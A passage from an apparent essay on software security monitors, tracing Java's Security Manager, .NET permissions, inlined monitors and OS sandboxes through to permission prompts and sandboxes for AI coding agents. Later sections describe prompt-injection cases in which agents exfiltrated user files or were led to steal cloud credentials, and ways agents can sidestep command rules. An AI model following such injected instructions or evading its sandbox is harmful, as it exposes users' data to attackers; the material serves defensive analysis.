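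OpenJDK states that the Security Manager could not address 19 of the 25 most dangerous software weaknesses on a 2020 industry list. For example, an XML document can make a careless program fetch a secret file, and Java needed separate protection against this in its XML library. The figure makes the Security Manager look somewhat worse than it was. The list is presumably the CWE Top 25, which covers all programming languages and includes memory errors that Java already prevents. A sandbox can also limit the damage after an attacker exploits a weakness that it could not prevent.

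### The end of both systems

Oracle disabled the Security Manager in Java 24, released in March 2025. Trying to switch it on from the command line now produces an error, and the program doesn't start.

.NET's system had gone through a similar decline earlier. It gave code different permissions depending on where the code came from, which surprised developers. Microsoft's *Security Policy in the v4 CLR* describes a common complaint that a program worked on its developer's machine but colleagues couldn't run it from a network folder, because code from there received fewer permissions. MSDN Magazine (2009) called the policy system "powerful but difficult to use and even more difficult to get right". Microsoft then simplified it in .NET Framework 4 and left it out of .NET Core, the redesigned version of .NET.

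Removing the permission system created a hazard for a time. To let existing code compile, .NET Core kept many of the old permission classes, but their checks did nothing. A library that required its callers to hold a permission would therefore accept every caller. Microsoft describes this as failing open, and in .NET 5 it made most of these classes produce a compiler warning. The old .NET Framework still contains the permission system, but Microsoft no longer treats it as a security boundary and won't fix ways to escape from it.

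*What is New in ASP.NET 4.0 Code Access Security* reports that most web-hosting companies ran their customers' sites under "Medium Trust" to keep one site from harming another. Medium Trust was a predefined set of Code Access Security permissions that a hosting company could choose from a list and apply to thousands of sites. Microsoft's SharePoint 2007 also relied on Code Access Security, and its developers had to understand permissions that, according to *SharePoint Administrator's and Developer's Guide to Code Access Security*, many other .NET developers could ignore.

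### The case for keeping the Security Manager

Java's plan to remove the Security Manager met organised opposition. A protest site, *Discuss JEP 411*, argued that most applications don't need everything Java lets them do, such as compiling new code while they run, and that a policy file can deny the unneeded abilities to an attacker.

In *Why JEP 411 Will Have a Negative Impact on Java Security*, Firmstone argues that nearly every Java program uses other people's libraries, and that without the Security Manager each library has all the program's permissions. He concedes that most developers stop once they see how hard it is to find the right permissions, and that the most determined give up when they notice the loss of speed. He recommends free tools that solve both problems, including one that records the permissions a program uses and writes the policy file.

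A longer article on the same site, Foojay's *JEP 411* (2021), says a generated policy has around 1,000 entries for 250,000 lines of code. Its author blames the Security Manager's poor reputation on the habit of granting `AllPermission` and on the documentation that recommended it. The article also suggests that companies, governments and armed forces use the Security Manager without saying so publicly.

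Oracle's team had partly answered this in the Inside Java post. It is hard to tell whether a very large set of permissions protects as intended, and the set has to be worked out again after each update. At a minute per entry, reviewing 1,000 entries takes almost 17 hours. Firmstone himself advises a separate policy for each Java release. Policies recorded from behaviour can also miss code that runs only once a year, a weakness Erlingsson found. The Inside Java post favoured limiting the whole process from outside, for example with containers. Such limits can't give two libraries in one program different permissions, so the disagreement is about whether that ability is worth the work of maintaining the policies.

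NetBeans, a program for writing Java software, used a custom Security Manager for a narrower purpose, to stop plug-ins from calling `System.exit`, which would close the editor. Apache NetBeans' *JEP 411* accepted gradual removal of the Security Manager but objected that no existing version of NetBeans would start under the changes proposed for Java 17. In the final plan, the Security Manager kept working in Java 17, and the incompatible change came in Java 18.

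For cases like this one, Oracle recommends rewriting code. Oracle's *The Security Manager Is Permanently Disabled* includes a sample program that changes an application's classes as they load. It looks for this instruction:

```
invokestatic java/lang/System.exit(I)V
```

It replaces the instruction with code that raises an error:

```
new           java/lang/RuntimeException
dup
ldc           "System.exit not allowed"
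invokespecial java/lang/RuntimeException.<init>(Ljava/lang/String;)V
athrow
```

This is a small inlined reference monitor, and it has the same gap as SASI's example. An application can also exit by calling `Runtime.getRuntime().exit(0)`, which the sample doesn't check for. The Security Manager caught both calls because its check was inside the method they eventually run. The sample is enough for a plug-in that calls `System.exit` by mistake, but not for one written to close the editor deliberately.

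### A rival with some of the same faults

If the Security Manager had satisfied the demand for configurable monitors, many people would have used it. Its low use suggests that something discouraged people from both. Not all of its faults carry over, however:

| Obstacle | Security Manager | Configurable inlined monitors |
|---|---|---|
| someone must write a policy for each program | yes | yes, though one policy can serve many programs |
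| updates can make the policy wrong | yes | yes |
| users must switch it on or install it | yes | yes |
| no partial policies | yes | no, SASI, Naccio and Polymer could restrict a few events and ignore the rest |
| permissions spread from library to application | yes | no, unless the policy imitates stack inspection |
| the platform's maintainers must support it | yes | no, the monitor's developers do this work |

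The first three obstacles could plausibly have held back both the Security Manager and inlined monitors. The next two are specific to the Security Manager's design and may have been enough to make it fail on their own. If so, its failure is weaker evidence about inlined monitors than it seems. SASI's version of the Security Manager ran about as fast as the original, so speed doesn't distinguish the two approaches.

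The built-in checks could also have discouraged competitors even if few developers used them. A software company had little reason to build a product that competed with a free part of Java, and a manager who had struggled with policy files might have dismissed anything similar. This is plausible, particularly since Java 1.2 arrived only months before SASI and Naccio, but there is no record of a company turning down an inlined monitor for this reason. The removal of the Security Manager partly tests the explanation, because some search servers that had relied on it switched to inlined monitors. However, those projects already had policies and people to maintain them, so they aren't typical of developers who never used the Security Manager or an inlined monitor.

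### The demand that disappeared with applets

Another explanation is that few people needed to confine Java code once applets were gone. OpenJDK deprecated the applet interface in 2017, and in 2018 Oracle released its Java 11 without the browser plug-in that ran applets. Most Java code now runs on servers, where the company that runs a program usually trusts its authors and worries more about malicious data, which the Security Manager can do little to keep out.

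Other sources of untrusted Java code also disappeared. Companies once expected to run programs from several customers on one shared Java server. Eckenfels (2015) wrote in *Run-time configurable sandboxes*, a message to a Java mailing list, that nobody considered this any more now that each customer could have a container. Some early Java features were designed for programs that would send code to one another over the network, but Mullan and Buckley report that this practice was never widely adopted.

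Oracle could remove the Security Manager with little protest because demand for it had vanished. But applets were still in use when SASI, Naccio and PoET/PSLang appeared, so a lack of demand doesn't explain why these research monitors found no users. Applet users had a reason to want protection at the time, but they already had a built-in policy and would have gained little by writing another. The claim that Java left no room for inlined monitors is therefore somewhat persuasive for applets.

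Browsers still run strangers' code, but now as JavaScript and WebAssembly instead of Java applets, under rules that the browser's makers supply. Java programs also still contain a great deal of third-party library code, as Firmstone points out. But developers choose their libraries and tend to trust them, whereas an applet could run as soon as someone opened a web page.

### Allow, prompt or deny

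Software for AI agents now comes with permission checks of its own. Jin, Jiao and Tong (2026), in *Agentao*, describe a typical design. Agentao is a harness that runs on the user's machine, and it answers each proposed tool call with one of three decisions: allow it, deny it, or prompt the user. The user or the application chooses one of four modes:

| Mode | Typical behaviour |
|---|---|
| read-only | allows reading and searching, denies everything else |
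| workspace-write | allows controlled edits to project files, prompts for broad shell or network use, denies destructive commands |
| full-access | allows ordinary tools but still stops high-risk actions |
| plan | allows planning and safe reading, denies changes |

The mode is only one part of the decision. Agentao works through these steps and stops at the first that settles the matter:

1. Deny the call if a built-in safety check rejects it.
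2. In read-only mode, deny any tool not marked as read-only.
3. Deny the call if it matches a restriction set for this run.
4. Follow the first matching rule from the user or the application.
5. Follow the first matching rule of the current mode.
6. If no rule matches, prompt if the tool is marked as needing confirmation, and otherwise allow the call.

The user's rules come before the mode, so they can override it. Suppose a user in workspace-write mode adds a rule to avoid prompts, allowing any command that starts with `python3`. If the agent then proposes `python3 setup.py`, the script runs whatever it contains, even though the mode would have prompted. Similarly, a user's rule that allows file edits would override plan mode unless the rule itself tests for the mode.

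Agentao avoids two of the Security Manager's faults. Partial policies work, because a user can write one rule and leave everything else to the mode. Permissions don't spread from a tool to its callers, because Agentao checks each call without inspecting a stack. The larger change is the prompt. The Security Manager could only allow or refuse, so someone had to decide everything in advance, but Agentao can prompt the user when a decision is needed and show the actual command. Jin and colleagues give no figures on how people use Agentao, but there is a good deal of evidence about prompts in other agents.

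### What people do with prompts

Users of Claude Code approve almost all permission requests. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, from earlier in 2026, reported an approval rate of 93%, and by August the figure in Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) was 97%. Most commands are harmless and deserve approval, so a high rate doesn't prove carelessness. The same users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, so they evidently read some of what they are asked to approve.

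A better test is whether people stop a dangerous command. Anthropic had a research company hire 1,053 professional testers for what looked like a coding study. Partway through, one prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one, and 143 testers (13.6%) rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers weren't working on their own projects and had little to lose, so people may be more careful at work. Anthropic also has an interest in the result, because the same article promotes its automatic replacement for prompts.

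Two independent surveys also found that many people approve agents' actions without reviewing them closely. In *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) found that 47.7% of the software practitioners they surveyed believed they read permission requests carefully. Another 20.6% said they approve by default, and 33.6% said they had become less careful over time. One interviewee complained of having to click something every ten seconds. In *From Delegation to Action Approval*, Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) surveyed 203 developers and found that 64% often approved at least one type of action without close review. The share was almost as high, at 61%, among developers who carefully reviewed the agent's code. It was 70% among those who knew of a security incident or worrying practice and 43% among those who didn't, and a difference remained after adjusting for how much the developers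 used agents. Neither survey drew a random sample, and both rely on self-reports.

Some prompts don't give users enough information to decide. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 reports of agents damaging files. In 80 of them the user had switched to automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative. The study's example is `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but can run any code.

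Users who write rules instead tend to write very broad ones. In June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule to allow some shell commands. Anthropic reports that 5% allowed every shell command and another 43% allowed an interpreter such as Python, which is nearly as broad. If those are shares of all active users, as they appear to be, almost everyone who wrote a rule gave the agent something close to `AllPermission`. A quarter of interactive sessions started with prompts switched off entirely.

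Asking people to write a careful policy beforehand may not help. Salerno and colleagues describe an experiment by Yan in which 113 people supervised a simulated day of an agent's actions. Some wrote standing rules in advance, while others approved each action or had a model review it. The standing rules blocked less overreach than either alternative. Participants set most of their rules to "ask", so they still had to decide when prompted, and they approved most of the actions that went too far.

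Anthropic responded by supplying the policy itself. In auto mode, a second model judges the commands that simpler rules don't settle, using more than 20 built-in rules about what to block. Users can describe which systems they trust and add their own rules or exceptions, or keep the defaults. Claude Code sets aside rules such as "allow any Python command" in this mode, because they would let the riskiest commands bypass the second model. Auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands in the test with 1,053 people. An earlier version missed 17% of 52 risky actions from Anthropic's own work. Anthropic still recommends human review for important changes to live systems.

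### Whether agents have brought the demand back

Agents have recreated much of the danger that applets posed. An applet was a stranger's program running on the user's computer, whereas an agent is the user's own program that a stranger can cause to misuse the user's privileges through prompt injection. Agents also make serious mistakes without any attacker. Wu and colleagues cite surveys by the programming site Stack Overflow, in which 31% of developers used agents in 2025 and 59% did in a smaller follow-up in April 2026.

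Many of these developers want protection. In Wu and colleagues' survey, 63% required approval or a warning before risky actions, and 53% restricted what their agents could access. More than half said they would give agents more freedom if the agents' actions were limited, visible or reversible. The Security Manager never attracted this much interest outside the browser. But developers mostly want limits that work, and the broad rules in Claude Code suggest that few users want to write the limits themselves.

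Browser makers could satisfy the same demand for applets with one strict policy, because a useful applet needed very little access. A coding agent has to edit files, run programs and often use the network, so it couldn't work under a policy that strict. The supplied policy has to be looser and depend on the task, which makes its mistakes harder to predict. Some companies have accepted this. Anthropic reports that Garner Health made auto mode the default for all 550 employees and no longer depends on hand-compiled lists of permitted commands.

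## Operating-system sandboxes as a cheaper substitute

Oracle advised people who lost the Security Manager to restrict the whole process from outside, with limits that the operating system enforces. Buyers may have already reached the same conclusion about inlined monitors. An operating-system sandbox could have replaced an inlined monitor if it covered most of what buyers wanted, worked for programs in any language without changing them, and came from a supplier who kept it up to date. Most buyers would also need to have had little use for the finer policies that only an inlined monitor can enforce, or some of them would have paid for the monitor anyway.

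The Inside Java post makes a similar argument, using the example of two methods, `foo` and `bar`, that both write to a system configuration file. A simple sandbox has to allow both writes or block both. The Security Manager could block `foo` and allow `bar`, perhaps because `bar` writes the file safely. The post argues that this distinction isn't worth its complexity. Containers and virtual machines can't make it, but they restrict native code as well as Java code. Even simple sandboxes take some expertise, though. Amazon, according to the same post, uses formal methods to analyse the policy files for its sandboxes.

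### Four mechanisms and their dates

| Mechanism | What it limits | Examples | Common since |
|---|---|---|---|
| system-call filter | which system calls a process may make | seccomp on Linux | about 2012 |
| mandatory access control | which files, network ports and other processes a program may use, under rules its user can't override | SELinux, AppArmor | 2004 on Fedora, 2007 on Ubuntu |
| app sandbox | each app to its own files, plus whatever the user or the platform grants | iPhone and Android apps | 2008 |
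| container | a group of processes to its own view of files, processes and network | Docker | about 2014 |

*Sandboxing Adoption in Open Source Ecosystems* (Alhindi and Hallett, 2024) dates seccomp to 2005, but seccomp's first version let a process do little more than read and write files that were already open. Programmable filters arrived in 2012. Landlock, a newer Linux mechanism, lets an ordinary process restrict its own access to files and directories. Its developer presented it in 2017, and the Linux kernel has included it since 2021.

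Sandboxes can't explain why nobody used the first research monitors, because none of the four mechanisms was common in 1999, when SASI and Naccio appeared. At the time, a company that wanted to confine one program could run it under a separate user account or use `chroot`, a Unix command that hides most of the file system from a process. Sandboxes may explain why so few people revived the idea later.

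### What a sandbox sees and what it remembers

| | Inlined monitor | System-call filter | Mandatory access control | Container |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Events | anything recognisable in the code, such as one method call | system calls and their numeric arguments | uses of files, ports and processes | uses of anything outside the container |
| Memory of earlier events | whatever the policy stores | none | labels on processes and files, but no history | none |
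| Software to trust | rewriter, language runtime, kernel | kernel | kernel | kernel and container software |
| Typical breakage | the platform adds a method that the policy doesn't name | a library starts using a call that the filter blocks | a file has the wrong label or moves | a file or connection that the program needs is missing |

Operating-system sandboxes add less trusted code than inlined monitors do. A program with an inlined monitor already depends on the kernel, so having the kernel do the checks adds little to the trusted computing base. The kernel's memory also needs no extra protection from a hijacked program, which can't reach it without exploiting another flaw.

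System-call filters depend on the platform. In 2021 a new version of glibc, the C library that most Linux programs use, began creating threads with a newer system call, clone3. Docker's default filter didn't list clone3 and returned an error that glibc treated as final, so some programs in up-to-date containers couldn't start a thread. A policy from 1999 that blocks java.nio fails in the same way. But Docker's maintainers corrected one default filter for everyone, whereas each SASI policy writer would have had to correct their own. The example supports the claim that a sandbox's supplier maintains it, at least when customers keep the default policy.

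### Reading a file, then sending a message

SASI's example policy, "no messages sent after reading a file", shows what buyers give up with a system-call filter. A seccomp filter is a short program that the kernel runs at every system call. From the call's number and arguments, it produces a decision, such as to allow the call, return an error or kill the process. Alhindi and Hallett describe a filter that lets a process write only to its standard output. With libseccomp, a C library for building filters, the central rule looks like this:

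```
seccomp_rule_add(ctx, SCMP_ACT_ALLOW, SCMP_SYS(write), 1,
                 SCMP_A0(SCMP_CMP_EQ, STDOUT_FILENO));
```

The filter can compare numbers, but it can't read the text stored at an address. A program opens a file by passing the address of the file's name, so the filter can't distinguish `secrets.txt` from a harmless settings file. If the filter did look up the name, another thread could change it after the check and before the kernel opened the file.

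It also can't express the order of events. Let *A* be the set of calls, with their numeric arguments, that a filter allows. Because the filter considers each call alone, it allows a run exactly when every call in the run belongs to *A*. SASI's policy permits a run that only reads and a run that only sends, so *A* has to contain both calls. But then

$$\text{read} \in A \;\text{ and }\; \text{send} \in A \;\Rightarrow\; \text{read}\cdot\text{send} \in A^{*},$$

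where *A*\* is the set of all runs composed of calls in *A*. The filter allows the very run that the policy forbids. A fixed filter can ban reading or ban sending, but not one after the other.

A process can get closer by giving up rights as it runs. OpenBSD, a Unix system known for its attention to security, has a system call named `pledge` for this purpose. A program states which groups of system calls it will still need, and the kernel kills it if it uses any others:

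```
pledge("stdio rpath inet", NULL);  /* basics, reading files, network */
sock = connect_to_server();
send_report(sock);
close(sock);                       /* an open connection stays usable */
pledge("stdio rpath", NULL);       /* gives up the network for good */
fd = open("secrets.txt", O_RDONLY);
```

After the second `pledge`, the program can read the file but can't open a connection, which corresponds to the state hasRead in SASI's automaton. A process can't regain rights it has dropped, so the first call has to include `rpath` if the program is to read anything later. The state before the second call is therefore weaker than SASI's, because the program may read and send in any order. SASI's rewriter put the change of state before every file read, but here the programmer has to put it in the right place. `pledge` protects a well-meaning developer whose program an attacker might hijack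 later, but not a customer who distrusts the developer.

Real programs drop rights this way. Alhindi and Hallett describe xwallpaper, which starts on OpenBSD with six groups of rights, including files and network. It later keeps only `stdio`, the group for basic input and output. Its Linux version imitates this with two seccomp filters, the second of which lists the 69 system calls in OpenBSD's `stdio` group.

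Denying the network altogether is much simpler. With Docker it takes one option:

```
docker run --network none report-tool
```

The program can now read any file in the container but has no network connection through which to send it. It also can't send messages before reading a file, which SASI's policy would allow. Many programs lose almost nothing from this added restriction, because they read a settings file when they start and SASI would block every message after that. For these programs, the sandbox gives nearly the same protection without a rewriter or a policy language. Neither policy is usable for a mail program, which has to send messages after reading files.

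A user who wants to send email but keep a tax return private can use Landlock or mandatory access control to hide the file from the mail program. This doesn't work when one program legitimately needs both the file and the network, as accounting software might. The user then needs a monitor that tracks where the file's contents go, which is harder than enforcing SASI's example policy. Once sandboxes were common, buyers who needed only the example policy therefore had little reason to choose an inlined monitor.

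### How many packages sandbox themselves

If sandboxes had won because they were cheap and easy, most programs should use one. Between April and August 2023, Alhindi and Hallett searched the source code of packages for four open-source systems for calls to sandboxing functions. They also counted the processes using those functions right after a fresh installation started up:

| System | Packages | Call a sandbox directly | Depend on a package that does | Sandboxed processes after start-up |
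|---|---|---|---|---|
| Debian | 59,893 | 406 (0.68%) | 17.0% | 5 of 120 |
| Fedora | 63,706 | 396 (0.62%) | 37.3% | 16 of 137 |
| OpenBSD | 7,700 | 114 (1.48%) | 24.7% | 33 of 36 |
| FreeBSD | 30,763 | 43 (0.14%) | 45.2% | 3 of 47 |

Direct use was therefore almost as rare as CFI on Linux. Debian's total also includes 97 versions of Firefox, many of which differ only in language. The much larger shares for indirect use are hard to interpret, because a package counts even if it only occasionally runs the sandboxed OpenSSH client. No package used Landlock to build a sandbox, but that is weak evidence about demand, because Landlock was two years old and Debian 11's standard kernel didn't have it.

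Difficulty explains part of this. Alhindi and Hallett examined gmid, a small server, on several systems. Sandboxing it took 549 lines of code with seccomp, 96 with OpenBSD's tools and 28 with FreeBSD's Capsicum. Child processes inherit seccomp and Capsicum limits, so gmid's developer also had to split the server into two processes, one that listens for requests and one that runs scripts. Yet few of OpenBSD's add-on packages used a sandbox either, even though `pledge` takes very little code. Alhindi and Hallett suggest that a developer still has to know which system calls and files a program needs, and that this gets harder as the program grows. The Security Manager's users faced the same problem.

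In the usability study *Playing in the Sandbox* (2025), seven developers with seccomp experience each took a different approach to sandboxing the same application. The sample is small, but the result suggests that even experts have no standard method. Packagers also disagree. *A Study of Application Sandbox Policies in Linux* (2022) compared programs in Flatpak and Snap, two formats that package a desktop program with a sandbox policy, and found that some programs had a permission, such as file access, in one format but not the other. The study still concluded that both formats improve security.

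Korchagin's *Sandboxing in Linux with zero lines of code* shows how to apply seccomp to any Linux program, including a proprietary one, without changing it. However, Salaün (2024), Landlock's developer, argues that policies written separately from a program end up unnecessarily broad, and designed Landlock so that developers could write and maintain a tighter policy with the program itself. Sandboxing a program without changing it therefore seldom produces a tight policy.

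The package counts leave out sandboxes applied from outside the program, which are the ones most people use. Every iPhone app runs in a sandbox, and a great deal of server software runs in containers. On a smaller scale, OpenBSD's own developers added the restrictions to its start-up processes. Sandboxes became common where a platform supplied or imposed them and stayed rare where each developer had to write a policy. Coarse, ready-made sandboxes could therefore well have drawn users away from inlined monitors, but carefully written seccomp filters probably didn't, since hardly anyone wrote one.

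### Splitting one program into parts

An inlined monitor can give two libraries in the same program different permissions. An operating system can do the same if a developer splits the program into processes with different rights. OpenSSH adopted this design in the early 2000s, and its success should have encouraged others.

*SoK: Software Compartmentalization* (Lefeuvre, Dautenhahn and colleagues, 2024) reviewed 211 research efforts and 61 mainstream systems that divide a program in this way. It calls adoption inconsistent and says compartmentalization is still far from common engineering practice. It gives the example of cryptography software, where researchers have recommended isolating secret keys for years but the leading libraries have no viable way to do it. Systems that are compartmentalized rely mostly on manual work and older, heavyweight mechanisms instead of the tools researchers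 have built.

Researchers have blamed poor automation, slow or limited mechanisms and weak guarantees, and Lefeuvre and colleagues think all of these play a part. They also identify a trade-off that automation doesn't remove. A tool that divides a program automatically can track which code uses which data but can't identify which data are confidential, so it may leave a secret accessible to untrusted code. A developer can supply that information, but only by writing a policy.

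The survey excludes containers and sandboxes around whole applications, so it doesn't show that those are rare. But if many buyers badly wanted different permissions for different parts of a program, more developers would presumably have used the operating system's tools to provide them. Either demand is small, or people are discouraged by the work of defining the parts, which any mechanism would require. In either case, an inlined monitor would have struggled to gain adoption even without competition from sandboxes.

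### System-call monitors that moved into the process

A monitor that must remember earlier system calls or inspect their contents needs more than a seccomp filter. The traditional solution is a separate monitoring process. Each check then requires context switches that inlining avoids, and their overhead adds up in a program that makes many system calls.

*Secpoline* (Sturm, Schelfhout and colleagues, 2026) reports that practice has shifted towards monitors inside the program's own process. These are inlined reference monitors whose events are system calls. A tool replaces each system-call instruction, or the library function around it, with a jump to the monitor's code. The monitor can then inspect the call without switching processes, and for some network traffic it can bypass the kernel altogether.

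Moving the monitor into the program's process gives up the kernel's separation of their memory. A hijacked program can overwrite an ordinary in-process monitor's code or data. Giving the program and monitor separate copies of the libraries doesn't fully solve this, because they still share the dynamic linker, which loads and connects libraries. The linker keeps a table of where each thread's private variables are. By changing an entry, an attacker can make the monitor use a different value without touching the original variable.

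Secpoline restores the separation in several steps:

1. It loads the monitor and the program as two executables in one process, each with its own dynamic linker and libraries.
2. It marks the monitor's memory with a protection key, a processor feature that can make chosen memory inaccessible while the program runs and accessible again when the monitor takes over.
3. It filters the program's code for instructions that would undo this protection, since a program can change its own access to protection keys without the kernel's help.
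4. It runs a small second monitor that checks the first one's system calls, so that ordinary software can serve as the monitor without changes.

In one test, Sturm and colleagues put ProxySQL, which relays requests to databases, inside the application's process and increased throughput by roughly 50% compared with the usual practice of running them as separate processes. The design still depends on the kernel, the hardware and the monitor's code having no exploitable bugs.

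Inlining is therefore sometimes the faster option, the reverse of the usual complaint about SASI. But much of the demand that Sturm and colleagues describe comes from fast networking and data processing, not from people who want to write security policies. A simple seccomp filter also runs inside the kernel without a second process, so speed gives users with simple policies no reason to stop relying on the operating system's sandbox.

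### The sandboxes that ship with coding agents

Coding agents have made sandboxes much more visible. As Cornelißen (2026), in *Agenten-Sandbox*, points out, GitHub Copilot, Claude Code, Codex and Cursor now all have one built in. The makers describe similar limits for the commands that an agent runs:

| Product | Limits on commands | Mechanism |
|---|---|---|
| Codex (OpenAI) | read almost anywhere, write in the project folder, no network | Seatbelt on macOS, bubblewrap on Linux, OpenAI's own sandbox on Windows |
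| Claude Code (Anthropic) | read, write in the project folder, no network without approval | Seatbelt on macOS, bubblewrap on Linux |
| Zed, a code editor | no writes outside the project or to its `.git` folder, no network | Seatbelt on macOS, bubblewrap on Linux and in Windows' Linux subsystem |

Seatbelt is macOS's built-in sandbox, and bubblewrap is a Linux program that starts a command with a restricted view of the system. In all three products, the agent or user can ask for more access when a task needs it.

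Subprocesses are a major reason for preferring these limits to rules about commands. NVIDIA explains that a check on tool calls can inspect a command before it starts but cannot control the processes the command launches. Zed gives the example of a rule that bans any command beginning with `git`. An agent can get around it by running `bash -c 'git ...'`, writing a small script, or using Python. A limit on writes to the `.git` folder stops all of these, because the operating system applies it to every process the command starts. *Agent Sandboxing* says Cursor's developers chose a sandbox over very detailed lists of allowed commands.

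The sandboxes also reduce interruptions. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports 84% fewer permission prompts with Claude Code's sandbox. Cursor, which described its own design in February 2026, says sandboxed agents stop 40% less often than unsandboxed ones. The two figures count different things, both come from the sandboxes' makers, and neither measures how many harmful actions the sandboxes prevented. Claude Code's users approve almost every prompt, and people reject fewer dangerous commands as prompts accumulate, so users may pay more attention to the prompts that remain.

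OpenAI built its own sandbox for Codex on Windows, a counterexample to the claim that the platform's supplier provides the sandbox. Wiesen explains in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows* that before that, Windows users had to approve nearly every command or let Codex do anything. He rejected three Windows features. AppContainer suits apps whose access needs are known in advance, but a coding agent may run any tool on the machine. Windows Sandbox opens a disposable desktop separate from the user's files and tools, and Windows Home doesn't include it. Using integrity levels would have let every low-trust process on the computer, not just Codex, write to the project folder.

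The first prototype limited file writes with a special identity that Windows checked in addition to the user's own. It restricted network access less securely, by changing settings so that common tools would try to connect through an address where nothing was listening. A program that ignored those settings could still reach the internet. Windows Firewall could block such a program, but it couldn't apply a rule only to the agent's commands while they ran under the user's account. OpenAI's current version therefore creates two extra Windows accounts, one with network access and one without, and runs commands under one of them. Installing this version requires an administrator's permission.

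That took substantial engineering, and OpenAI now has to maintain the result. Microsoft has since begun to offer more itself. In October 2026, Jaloza's *Bringing local models and sandboxed tools to Windows and GitHub Copilot* presented sandboxed tools for the two products, and Windows Blogs' *Microsoft Execution Containers* announced containment for agents on Windows 11. Codex users didn't have to build anything in either case, so the claim still holds for them if "supplier" includes the agent's maker.

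Ready-made sandboxes can also fail without the user noticing. NVIDIA's *Sandboxing Agents with AI Workbench* warns that an agent's sandbox may silently switch off inside a container that lacks the features it needs. Zed's developers describe an attack in which a user approves writes to `/foo/bar`, and the agent replaces that folder with a link to the user's home folder before the sandbox starts. Without a further check, the sandbox would make the home folder writable. Zed detects the change and refuses to run the command.

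### OpenShell's four layers

OpenShell, NVIDIA's sandbox for agents, combines operating-system limits with more detailed rules. NVIDIA's *OpenShell Security Best Practices for Controls, Risks, and Configuration Guidance* describes four layers:

| Layer | What enforces it | Can it change while the agent runs? |
|---|---|---|
| files | Landlock | no |
| processes | seccomp and an account with few privileges | no |
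| network | a proxy that checks each connection against a policy | yes |
| access to AI models | a proxy that directs requests to approved models | yes |

By default the network proxy blocks every connection. An operator allows a destination by naming the host, the port and the programs that may use it. A simplified rule might look like this:

```
github:
  endpoints:
    - host: api.github.com
      port: 443
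      protocol: rest         # inspect each web request
      access: read-only      # permit only requests that read
      enforcement: enforce   # block violations
  binaries:
    - path: /usr/bin/curl
```

Without the `protocol` line, the proxy checks only the host, port and program, then forwards whatever the agent sends. Without the `enforcement` line, it logs a forbidden request but lets it through. NVIDIA recommends starting in this logging mode and switching to blocking after checking the rules. That is sensible for testing, but if the operator forgets to switch, the proxy will keep logging forbidden requests without blocking them.

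The operator now has to write a policy, which means finding out which hosts a task needs, whether a rule should cover reading or writing, and which program should have access. Operators can also approve new destinations as the agent requests them, and each approval lasts until someone destroys the sandbox. OpenShell reduces the work with presets such as `read-only`, but a sandbox takes the least work when the agent needs no network at all. OpenShell's network rules also keep no history, which is why Sistla and colleagues class them as stateless allowlists. Like seccomp, OpenShell therefore can't enforce SASI's example policy.

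### Harms that look like permitted actions

NVIDIA warns that an agent can leak data through any destination an operator allows. Anthropic's Claude Cowork, an agent for office work that runs code in a virtual machine, had this problem. The machine could connect to Anthropic's own servers because the product needs them. Someone who reported the flaw put a file with hidden instructions in the user's folder, along with a key to an attacker's Anthropic account. Claude followed the instructions and uploaded other files from the folder to that account. The proxy allowed the upload because the address was approved, so the data leaked even though, in Anthropic's words, the sandbox "worked perfectly."

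Anthropic fixed the problem with a second proxy that reads requests to its servers and rejects any that don't carry the key issued to that virtual machine. The proxy checks whose account receives the data, which can't be specified in a list of addresses.

Sandboxes can also stop attacks that a model fails to refuse. In a February 2026 exercise, an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into pasting instructions into Claude Code. The instructions would steal the employee's cloud credentials, and Claude complied in 24 of 25 trials because the request seemed to come from its user. Anthropic concludes that only limits on files and network connections would reliably stop this attack.

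A sandbox is less useful when an agent acts through tools on other people's servers. Suppose that an agent in an accounts department may use the company's mail server, and it sends one customer's invoice to another. The operating system handles an encrypted connection from a permitted program to a permitted host, just as it does for a correct email. The table compares this case with others, assuming a sandbox with a short list of approved hosts and a policy layer that reads the arguments of each tool call:

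| Harm | Sandbox | Agent policy layer |
|---|---|---|
| a script deletes files outside the project | blocks it | may see only the script's name |
| a script uploads credentials to an unknown host | blocks it | may see only the script's name |
| the agent deletes useful files inside the project | allows it, unless deletion is off | can block a call to a delete tool |
| an invoice goes to the wrong customer | allows it | can block it if it knows whose invoice it is |
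| the agent refunds $2,000 instead of $20 | allows it | can block refunds above a limit |
| the right customer receives misleading advice | allows it | allows it, unless something judges the text |

The sandbox is stronger in the first two rows, and the policy layer is stronger in the next three. Neither helps much in the last row, where the harm comes entirely from what the text means.

Zed's developers point out that an agent can add a build script to a project without leaving its sandbox. If the user builds the project in an ordinary terminal after the agent has finished, the script runs with all the user's privileges. Zed's sandbox also doesn't cover the agent's file-editing tool or MCP servers.

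How much an agent still needs a policy layer therefore depends on what it does. A coding agent that works on local files and has no network access needs few rules beyond its sandbox, except for rules about its edits. An agent that sends email, issues refunds or changes customer records needs many, because most of its harmful actions use the same connections as its useful ones. No one seems to have measured how incidents divide between these two kinds of agent.

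Sandbox makers have not treated sandboxes as a complete substitute. OpenAI's *Sandbox* describes sandboxing and approvals as different controls that work together, and OpenAI adds a list of permitted network destinations and an automatic reviewer when its own staff use Codex. Java's developers agreed less about how far to rely on the operating system, and the maintainers of the search server Solr argued over it when they lost the Security Manager.

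## Who writes the policy and answers for it

Even a good policy sometimes stops legitimate work. Someone then has to find out whether the program or the rule is at fault, and change one of them. If that is nobody's job, people will probably switch the monitor off.

Every monitor involves four roles: writing the policy, maintaining it, benefiting from the protection, and taking the blame when a program breaks. The policy's owner is the party that takes on the writing, maintenance and blame. The ownership argument is that inlined monitors went unused where different parties held the four roles, because the people who would have done the work gained little from it.

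### Who holds the roles in four cases

| | Writes the policy | Pays for upkeep | Benefits | Gets the blame |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Research monitor such as Naccio | an expert or administrator | nobody in particular | whoever runs the program | the administrator or the program's developer |
| Control-flow integrity in Windows or Android | the platform's maker, through its compiler | the platform's maker | users and the platform's maker | the platform's maker |
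| Phone app permissions | the platform's maker defines them, the developer requests them, the user grants them | the platform's maker and the developer | the user | mostly the developer |
| Employer's app wrapping | the employer | the employer and the wrapping tool's vendor | the employer | the employer and the app's developer |

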